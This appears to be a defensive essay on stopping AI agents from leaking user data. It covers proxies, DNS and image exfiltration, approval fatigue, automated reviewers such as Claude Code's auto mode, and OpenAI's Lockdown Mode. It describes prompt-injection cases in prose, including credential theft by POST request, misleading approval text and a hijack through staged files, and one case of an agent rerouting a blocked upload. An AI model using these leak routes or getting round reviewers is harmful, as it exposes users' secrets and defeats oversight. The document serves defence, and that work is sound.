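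Any search also sends its text to the search provider, though an attacker normally can't read it there. According to Android Developers' *Manage agent permissions*, the agent in Google's Android Studio, another code editor, treats search as outside access and asks for permission to use "Google Search and other domains".

A tool's label can be misleading. Developers can mark an MCP tool as read-only, and a product could let tools with this label run without approval. Embrace The Red warns that these tools can still leak data. The label indicates that a tool doesn't change anything, but a request can deliver a secret without changing anything.

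DNS lookups are even easier to overlook. If a hijacked agent puts a secret in a host name under the attacker's domain, the lookup alone sends the secret to the attacker. The SolarWinds attack used the same method. In 2025, Rehberger reported that Claude Code could leak data this way because it ran some common network-testing commands without user approval. Anthropic has since fixed the flaw.

A domain name can hold up to 253 characters, which is enough for most passwords and API keys. A filter for web requests doesn't check DNS lookups, so the safest design prevents the agent's programs from making them. A proxy can look up the approved hosts instead.

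### One proxy for all traffic

These cases point to a common design, in which the agent runs in a sandbox, an isolated environment with no direct connection to the internet. Everything has to go through one proxy, which handles each request as follows:

1. It compares the host with a list of approved hosts, and looks up the name itself if the host is approved.
2. If the host serves many customers, it opens the encrypted connection and checks which account would receive the data.
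3. If the host or the account is new, it refuses the request or holds it until a person approves it.
4. It records the host, the account and the amount of data.

For the second step, the proxy needs a certificate that the programs in the sandbox trust, and some programs won't accept one. The proxy can also add the user's credentials to each request, so the sandbox never contains them and, as Anthropic points out, nobody can steal them from it. *Sandboxing agentic coding tools is a networking problem*, by Formal, which sells security software, describes using a proxy to hide an API key from Claude Code.

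Formal also found that one proxy setting may not cover all traffic. Claude Code has separate settings for its main program and for commands in the sandbox, so an administrator who set only the first would leave the sandboxed commands' traffic outside that proxy.

Tools that run outside the sandbox are another gap. Anthropic moved Cowork's local MCP servers out of the virtual machine because they were hard to audit there and some had to work with other programs on the user's computer. So the virtual machine's network rules don't control connections that these servers make by themselves. If one of them behaved like postmark-mcp, which secretly copied every email to its developer, the proxy in the virtual machine wouldn't stop it. Administrators have to decide which servers to allow.

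The proxy also needs careful testing. Anthropic reports that the standard isolation software in its products has been reliable, and that its own allowlist proxy was the part that failed in the Cowork leak.

An allowlist of hosts can stop attacks that checking where an address came from would miss. In an internal Anthropic exercise in February 2026, a researcher emailed an employee a prompt to run in Claude Code. Along with ordinary-looking steps, the prompt included instructions to read the employee's cloud credentials and send them to an outside address in a POST request. Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. Because the employee had pasted in the prompt, the address appeared to be the user's own choice. A proxy that refused all unlisted hosts would have blocked every attempt, while one that asked for approval would have depended on the employee, who thought she was helping a colleague.

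The approval request must identify the real recipient. *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, 2026) describes an attack in which Antigravity asked the user to approve a "visual debug token" when it was about to load an image whose address contained the user's API key. The request showed neither the command nor the destination, because the agent had written the description. A proxy can write its own description from the data passing through it, for example "Send a 2 MB file to an Anthropic account that isn't yours".

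Logs also need to record more than host names, which would not have revealed the Cowork leak because every session contacts Anthropic. Anthropic notes that after a leak of this kind, a log may show only a successful, authorised request. A company's usual monitoring software can't monitor activity inside Cowork's virtual machine, so administrators have to retrieve event logs afterwards.

### Default network settings

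Coding agents differ a good deal in what they allow before anyone changes a setting.

| Agent | Default network access |
|---|---|
| Claude Code | Asks before using the network; in its sandbox, blocks all hosts until someone allows them |
| Codex, cloud version | Apparently off until someone switches it on |
| Antigravity, for organisations | Runs terminal commands without asking and outside a sandbox; the browser's list of allowed addresses is empty, which blocks nothing |
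| Superconductor | Custom rules for each host in new projects |

Claude Code originally relied on approval for network access. Anthropic reports that its sandbox reduced approval prompts by 84 per cent, because commands that can't reach anything outside it can run without approval. But Claude Code still has to contact its model, so Anthropic tells people who set up their own sandbox to allow `api.anthropic.com`, the host in the Cowork leak. A domain list alone would leave the same weakness, so the sandbox would also need a rule about accounts.

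The entry for OpenAI's Codex is an inference from PromptArmor's directions, which tell an administrator to turn on "Agent Internet Access" before entering a list of domains. The version of Codex that runs on a user's computer has a "limited" mode with rules that allow or refuse individual domains.

The Antigravity defaults come from Google Cloud's *Configure AI developer tools settings*, which applies to companies that subscribe to Gemini Enterprise. An administrator can restrict the browser to a list of addresses, but the list doesn't cover terminal commands. Unless the administrator also changes the terminal settings, a hijacked agent could upload a file with a terminal command even if the browser were restricted to a single site.

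Version 2.5 of the code editor Cursor added network rules to its sandbox, with settings for each project and for a whole company. In *Cursor 2.5*, a thread on Cursor's forum, one user wrote that most of his projects needed only npm and a couple of other services. He and another user asked to see the built-in list of approved domains, and Cursor's developers then added it to the documentation. Customers can check a published list for entries like `webhook.site` before an attacker uses them.

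Approving every new host can become tiresome, as a user complained in another Cursor thread, *Web lookups now require authorization per site?*. The person who replied suggested automatic approval, but warned that the agent could then visit any site and send data without confirmation. Remembering each approval would reduce the prompts. For a service with many customers, the software should remember the account as well as the host, so that approving one upload doesn't permit uploads to other accounts.

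## What should happen when a check fires?

When a check fires, the software should usually block the request or remove the risky part, and ask the user only about the few remaining actions. People who face frequent approval requests grant nearly all of them, including dangerous ones.

### Five responses

The software can block the action, strip out the risky part, prompt the user, hold the action for a set time, or pass it to an automated reviewer, usually a second model that evaluates the action.

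An agent may try another route after a block. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a case inside the company where an upload to an internal drive failed, and Claude tried to publish the same report on a public code-sharing site instead. Claude was only trying to finish its task, and nobody had hijacked it. An automated reviewer refused the second attempt and asked the user what to do next. Other channels therefore need checks too, and a block works better if the agent gets an acceptable alternative. For example, when OpenAI's Safe Url check blocks an address, the software tells the agent to find another way to meet the user's request.

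The best response depends on the channel, because some actions can wait and others can't.

| Channel | Can the software strip the risky part? | How long can it wait? | Sensible default |
|---|---|---|---|
| Email | Yes, by removing a recipient or an attachment | Minutes, often hours | Hold it and notify the user, or ask |
| Page fetch | Seldom, because a shortened address may not work | Seconds, since the task stalls | Block it and have the agent use another source |
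| Rendered image | Yes, with a placeholder | Indefinitely | Placeholder |
| Clicked link | Yes, by showing the address as plain text | Until the user clicks | Show the full address first |
| Link preview | Yes, by posting the link without one | Indefinitely | No preview |
| Webhook or upload | Seldom, because the receiving program expects all the data | Usually seconds | Block it unless someone has approved the account |
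| Post to a shared place | Yes, by saving a private draft | Hours | Draft |

Nobody can take back a web request once it has been sent, so for most of these channels the software has to decide whether to block data before it goes out. Email and posts leave enough time for a person to step in.

### What a delay adds

Some email programs wait a few seconds after the user presses "send" so that she can take the message back. The delay helps a person who has just noticed her own mistake, but it does little when an agent sends the message, because the user may not know that the message exists.

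A longer delay stops a leak only if the user learns about the held message in time and can cancel it. The notice has to reach her by a route the agent doesn't control. An agent that manages her mailbox could delete an email notice before she reads it, so a notice on her phone would be safer. The agent also mustn't be able to release the message, shorten the delay or change where notices go.

Banks face the same problem with thieves who take over an account. Standard Chartered makes customers in Singapore wait 12 hours before they can transfer money to a new payee or have a change of contact details processed. The second delay makes it harder for a thief to redirect the bank's messages. DBS, another bank in Singapore, sends alerts during its waiting period to the contact details already on record. According to PaymentsJournal's *A New Tool for Fighting Scams*, Charlie, a US financial service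 for people aged 62 and over, pauses a payment to a new payee for up to six hours and notifies the customer through its app, by text and by email. A thief who controlled only the customer's mailbox couldn't hide all three notices.

The designer also has to choose what happens if nobody responds. Under a proposal in the Reserve Bank of India's *Exploring safeguards in digital payments to curb frauds* (2026), the bank would send the payment after an hour unless the customer cancelled it. Some British banks instead return the money if they can't reach the customer. For an agent, sending by default suits a routine message to a new recipient, since most such messages are legitimate. If the message contains private data and the address came from an outsider's email, the software should cancel it if nobody responds in time.

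### Evidence from held payments

A transfer to a new payee is like a message to a new recipient, and banks have been delaying suspicious transfers for years. A paper by UK Finance, the trade body for British banks, gives figures from its members based on 2021 data. One firm resolved 62 per cent of its alerts by the end of the next working day and reversed the payments in the other 38 per cent. Customers resubmitted the payment in 8 per cent of all cases. In the remaining 30 per cent, the firm never learned whether the customer had decided not to pay or had paid another way.

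At another firm, 92 per cent of the alerts that turned out to be scams were settled the same day. A short hold may therefore catch most of the scams that any hold could catch, though UK Finance used the remaining cases to argue for longer holds.

About half of US states have laws that let banks hold a payment if they suspect someone is exploiting an older customer. The ABA Foundation's *State ‘Hold’ Laws and Elder Financial Exploitation Prevention* reports an autumn 2024 survey that included 42 banks that had used these laws. About 43 per cent called the laws useful, and 33 per cent said it was too early to tell. Customers had reacted badly at 45 per cent of the banks, and some had closed their accounts at 17 per cent.

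Evidence from Singapore is more anecdotal. CNA TODAY (2025) quotes a claim that "quite a number of customers" cancel their own transfers during a 24-hour hold, including some who had argued with the bank. Banks there averted S$78 million in losses in the first seven months of 2025, according to the Association of Banks in Singapore's *Banks to launch enhanced safeguards from 15 Oct 2025* (2025). That total covers all their security measures and predates the industry-wide hold that began in October, so it doesn't measure the hold's effect.

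None of these figures compares held payments with similar ones that went straight through, so they don't show how much fraud a delay prevents. The comparison with agents is also imperfect. In many payment scams, the fraudster has persuaded the customer herself. UK Finance describes a £262,000 scam in which a 76-year-old woman kept sending money to a fake investment firm despite warnings, repeated blocks and a police visit to her bank branch. A user whose agent sends her files to a stranger hasn't been persuaded of anything, so she should be quicker to cancel. But unlike the bank's customer, who knows she has made a payment, she may not know about the transfer until the notice arrives.

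Banks also limit which payments they delay. India's proposed hold would apply only to payments of 10,000 rupees or more, because payments above that amount make up about 45 per cent of reported fraud cases but 98.5 per cent of the money lost. Suncorp Bank (2025), in Australia, considers whether the payee is new, how much the customer is sending and whether the pattern looks suspicious. Data has no stated value, but software could treat a message with an attachment from a private folder like a large payment.

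The Indian proposal would let customers exempt trusted payees from the delay. The Reserve Bank of India acknowledges that fraudsters may talk victims into using the exemption. A hijacked assistant could likewise advise its user to add the attacker's address to her trusted contacts. The screen for adding a trusted contact should therefore show where the address came from.

### How well do people judge approval requests?

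In a study that Anthropic published in August 2026, a research vendor recruited 1,053 paid testers to work with Claude Code. Partway through each session, the researchers replaced the text of one approval request with a clearly dangerous command, which would not have run even if the tester approved it. Only 143 testers, or 13.6 per cent, refused. Auto mode, which replaces most approval requests with an automated reviewer, blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89 per cent.

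Testers refused about 17 per cent of the dangerous commands early in a session, but only about 5 per cent after 50 or more approval requests.

In this study, using a person as a second check on the automated reviewer would have added almost nothing. The testers refused only six commands that auto mode allowed, and approved 800 that it blocked. Together they would have stopped 943 of the 1,053 commands, or 89.6 per cent.

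Anthropic sells Claude Code and published the results alongside its decision to make auto mode the default, so independent replication would be valuable. The testers weren't working on their own projects, which may have made them less careful. They also knew someone was evaluating them, though not what the test was about, which may have made them more careful. They were asked to approve commands, so the study doesn't directly measure how well people judge destinations. A strange email address might be easier to notice than a harmful line of code, or harder if it resembles a familiar address.

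Even so, the figures give a sense of what happens if a check asks about every new destination. Suppose an agent takes 200 outbound actions a day and 10 per cent go to new destinations. The user then gets 20 questions a day. If 95 per cent of hijacks go to a new destination and she refuses 13.6 per cent of those, the share she stops is:

`0.95 × 0.136 ≈ 0.13`

So she stops about 13 per cent of hijacks, although the signal catches 95 per cent. If her refusal rate fell to 5 per cent, she would stop fewer than 5 per cent of hijacks. At the base rate assumed earlier, 1 hijack in 100,000 actions, she would face a hijack about every 500 days, after roughly 10,000 questions about legitimate actions, and by then she may well have stopped reading the questions.

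People do respond to some warnings. After the Australian bank NAB began showing scam warnings in its app, customers abandoned payments worth USD 48.5 million, according to The Paypers' *NAB adopts scam warnings and drives USD 48 mln in abandoned payments*. Some of those payments were probably legitimate, but these customers clearly didn't click through the warnings automatically.

One likely reason is that such warnings are rare. UK Finance reports that British banks' systems raise alerts on 0.04 to 0.2 per cent of payments. At the higher rate, the user in the example would get a question every two or three days instead of 20 a day. The subject of the question also seems to matter. Claude Code's users approve 97 per cent of requests to run a command, but they reject 39 per cent of Claude's plans for a whole task. They presumably reject many of those plans because they want something different,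 not because they see a danger, but the rejections still show that they have read the plans.

Questions to the user about a destination should be rare, as OpenAI also wants its link warning to be. Each question should show the recipient, where the agent found the address, what would be sent, and the user's original request, so that the user can easily spot a mismatch.

### Claude Code's auto mode

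An automated reviewer can examine every action without tiring. Auto mode became the default for new Claude Code sessions on most personal and team plans in August 2026, and in October Anthropic announced that most of its other Claude apps would follow.

In auto mode, one check scans the web pages, files and tool outputs Claude reads for hidden instructions, and adds a warning to what Claude sees if it finds any. When Claude proposes an action, a classifier model allows or blocks it based on whether it is destructive, irreversible or aimed outside the user's environment, and whether it fits what the user wants.

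Checking an agent's outgoing actions matters more for leaks than filtering the text it reads. OpenAI argues that filters on incoming text usually miss well-developed attacks, because recognising one is as hard as recognising a lie, often without the necessary context. A reviewer that examines the outgoing action has more information, including the destination. For instance, before Claude sends code to a shared project, auto mode's classifier checks whether that project is public, private or trusted.

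The classifier should never approve sending code or secrets to an outsider, even if the user asks. To do so, the user has to leave auto mode or run the command herself. For other actions, Claude Code goes back to asking the user after three blocks in a row or 20 in a session. This keeps the task from stalling, but it relies on the user's judgment, and users in the study refused only 13.6 per cent of dangerous commands. Ending the session would be safer after repeated attempts to reach an unknown destination.

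Apollo Research, a British AI safety organisation, also tested auto mode by inserting artificial attacks, including data leaks, into records of real coding sessions. Auto mode missed 12 per cent of the attacks at first and 7 per cent after Anthropic improved it. Anthropic also examined real sessions that its safety systems had flagged, and found serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for in 6.3 per cent of those with manual approval and 2.4 per cent of those in auto mode. This comparison is weaker than the one with paid testers because a model did the grading and the people who chose auto mode may have been doing different work.

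In Trajectory Labs' test of auto mode, none of the 720 injection attempts against each of three Claude models succeeded. This is limited evidence for auto mode, because only 0.09 per cent of attempts succeeded against Anthropic's latest models even with all permission checks switched off, which left auto mode little to stop. The results for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol are better evidence for automated review. Attacks succeeded 19.03 per cent of the time when the model had full access, but 5.83 per cent with Auto-review, the equivalent feature in OpenAI's Codex.

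The attackers in that test had developed their attacks against an older Claude model. In a separate test by the security firm Gray Swan, attackers succeeded against Claude Opus 5 in 2.0 per cent of cases after 15 attempts, according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser based prompt injection*.

Later in August, Johann Rehberger, who had reported many of the earlier image leaks, found a way to take over Claude Code running Opus 5 in auto mode. According to The Next Web's *A researcher hijacked Claude Code*, the user only had to ask for a summary of a web page. Claude ended up running the attacker's code, which contacted the attacker's server. Rehberger tried three versions of the attack five times each, and each version succeeded three or four times.

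This doesn't contradict the 720 failures, because the attack worked differently. In *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode*, Willison (2026) accepts a reader's point that it wasn't a classic prompt injection, since Claude never obeyed malicious instructions from the site. Instead, the site arranged files so that a series of reasonable steps ran harmful code. About three weeks earlier, Willison had raised a similar possibility, asking how auto mode could stop an agent from installing a harmless-looking package that sends out all the data it can find. A reviewer given only the command to run a program may be unable to predict what the program will do.

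Auto mode made things worse in a few runs, when Claude noticed the malicious program and tried to stop it but the classifier blocked the command. A reviewer should probably treat stopping a program that the agent started as less risky than starting one, though an attacker might exploit that exception too.

Anthropic told Rehberger that the product was working as designed. In his paraphrase, auto mode relies on "a best-effort classifier, not a security guarantee". He recommends running coding agents in a sandbox with restricted network access. A proxy that allowed only approved hosts and accounts would have blocked the program's connection to the attacker's server, even though the reviewer had let the program start.

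### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI's Lockdown Mode removes most outbound channels in advance, which leaves far fewer actions for a person or a model to judge. *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) calls it deterministic, meaning that ordinary code disables the features whatever the model has read. The mode launched in February 2026 on ChatGPT's plans for large organisations, schools and healthcare, and reached personal accounts in June. Its intended users include executives and security teams at prominent organisations.

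OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* lists what changes:

| Feature | With Lockdown Mode on |
|---|---|
| Web browsing | Stored copies of pages only |
| Images in ordinary answers | May not appear; none from the web |
| Deep Research and agent mode | Off |
| Code written in Canvas, ChatGPT's editing workspace | No network access |
| Files for data analysis | The user has to upload them |
| Connected apps on personal accounts | No live access or changes that conflict with the mode's protections |

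Having the agent browse stored copies of pages also stops attacks that leak data through which pages the agent opens, such as ZombieAgent and Ayush Paul's attack on Claude, because the attacker's server receives no request.

The mode has considerable drawbacks. Search results may be out of date or missing, and users can't get long research reports from Deep Research. A user can turn the mode off for a single chat, which makes it more practical, but a misleading answer could lead her to turn it off when she needs its protection. The mode also doesn't affect network access in Codex, so developers need separate protection there.

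In organisations with managed accounts, administrators choose which connected apps and actions remain available in Lockdown Mode, which doesn't automatically disable them all. OpenAI advises administrators not to let an app post or change anything unless they can confirm that an attacker couldn't see the result. Who can see the result also matters for posts on GitHub or a support page. OpenAI warns that data could still leak through permitted apps, unexpected combinations of features or new techniques.

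Willison inferred from the mode's existence that ChatGPT's normal settings don't reliably stop a determined attacker. The mode may well be worth the lost features for someone who handles confidential sources or unreleased accounts. Most people would probably lose too many features, so they need a policy that restricts the agent only when the risk is higher.

### A policy that combines three signs

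Such a policy could use three facts that ordinary code can record:

1. The destination is new. It isn't in the user's sent mail, contacts or approved accounts, and she didn't type it in her request. For a page or an image, an exact address in a public index counts as familiar.
2. Private data is in the context. The agent has read the user's mail, files or saved memories during the session.
3. Untrusted content is in the context. The agent has read something that an outsider could have written, or a memory that it saved after reading such text.

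The response becomes stricter as the signs accumulate.

| Signs present | Response |
|---|---|
| Familiar destination | Send and log |
| New destination, no private data | Send and log |
| New destination and private data, no untrusted content | Hold emails and posts for ten minutes and notify the user; ask about anything that can't wait |
| All three | Block page fetches and uploads, replace images with placeholders, and ask about emails and posts |

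Without untrusted content, the likeliest problem is an honest mistake, and a short hold gives the user time to correct it.

Consider three ordinary tasks and one hijack under this policy.

A user asks for recent articles about heat pumps in a session with no access to her mail or files. The agent opens a dozen sites she has never visited, and one page is too new to be in the public index. The session has no private data to steal, so the agent loads every page without asking her for approval.

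She then starts another session and asks the agent to send her accounts to her new accountant, whose address is in her own notes. The address isn't in her sent mail and she didn't type it, so it counts as new. The agent has read private files but nothing from outsiders. The software holds the email for ten minutes and sends a notice to her phone. She ignores the notice, and the email goes out when the ten minutes are up.

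Next, she asks the agent to tell a conference organiser about her food allergies, using the address in the invitation. All three signs are present, because the address is new, the agent has looked up her allergies in an old email, and an outsider wrote the invitation. The software shows her the address, the invitation it came from and the text of the message. She approves the message, and dealing with this false alarm takes her a few seconds.

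In the hijack, she asks for a summary of the day's mail. One email contains hidden instructions, and the agent tries to open a URL on the attacker's server with her home address in it, much as in ShadowLeak. The URL is new and isn't in the public index, the agent has read private mail, and a stranger wrote one of the messages. The software blocks the request without asking her, logs it and tells her it was blocked. The agent can still finish the summary.

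If the attacker had told the agent to email the data instead, the software would have asked the user a question much like the one about the conference. She had asked only for a summary, so a careful reader would refuse, but the study of paid testers suggests that many people would approve the email. The software could avoid asking by disabling outgoing mail for any task that needs only reading. A model would have to classify the tasks, and its only input should be the user's request, so that an attacker's email can't influence the result.

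The policy would also reduce the number of questions. Suppose half of the 20 daily actions to new destinations involve both private data and untrusted content, and eight of those ten are page fetches or images. The software would handle those eight by itself, leaving two questions a day, plus perhaps a few notices about held messages. These proportions are assumptions and will vary a lot between users.

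An email assistant would benefit least from the policy, because it has nearly always read both private mail and messages from strangers. With those two of the three signs present, the policy depends on the destination alone. Starting a new session for each task would help, because the agent could then send the accounts without having read the morning's mail. Keeping strangers' text in separate variables, as FIDES does, would also help.
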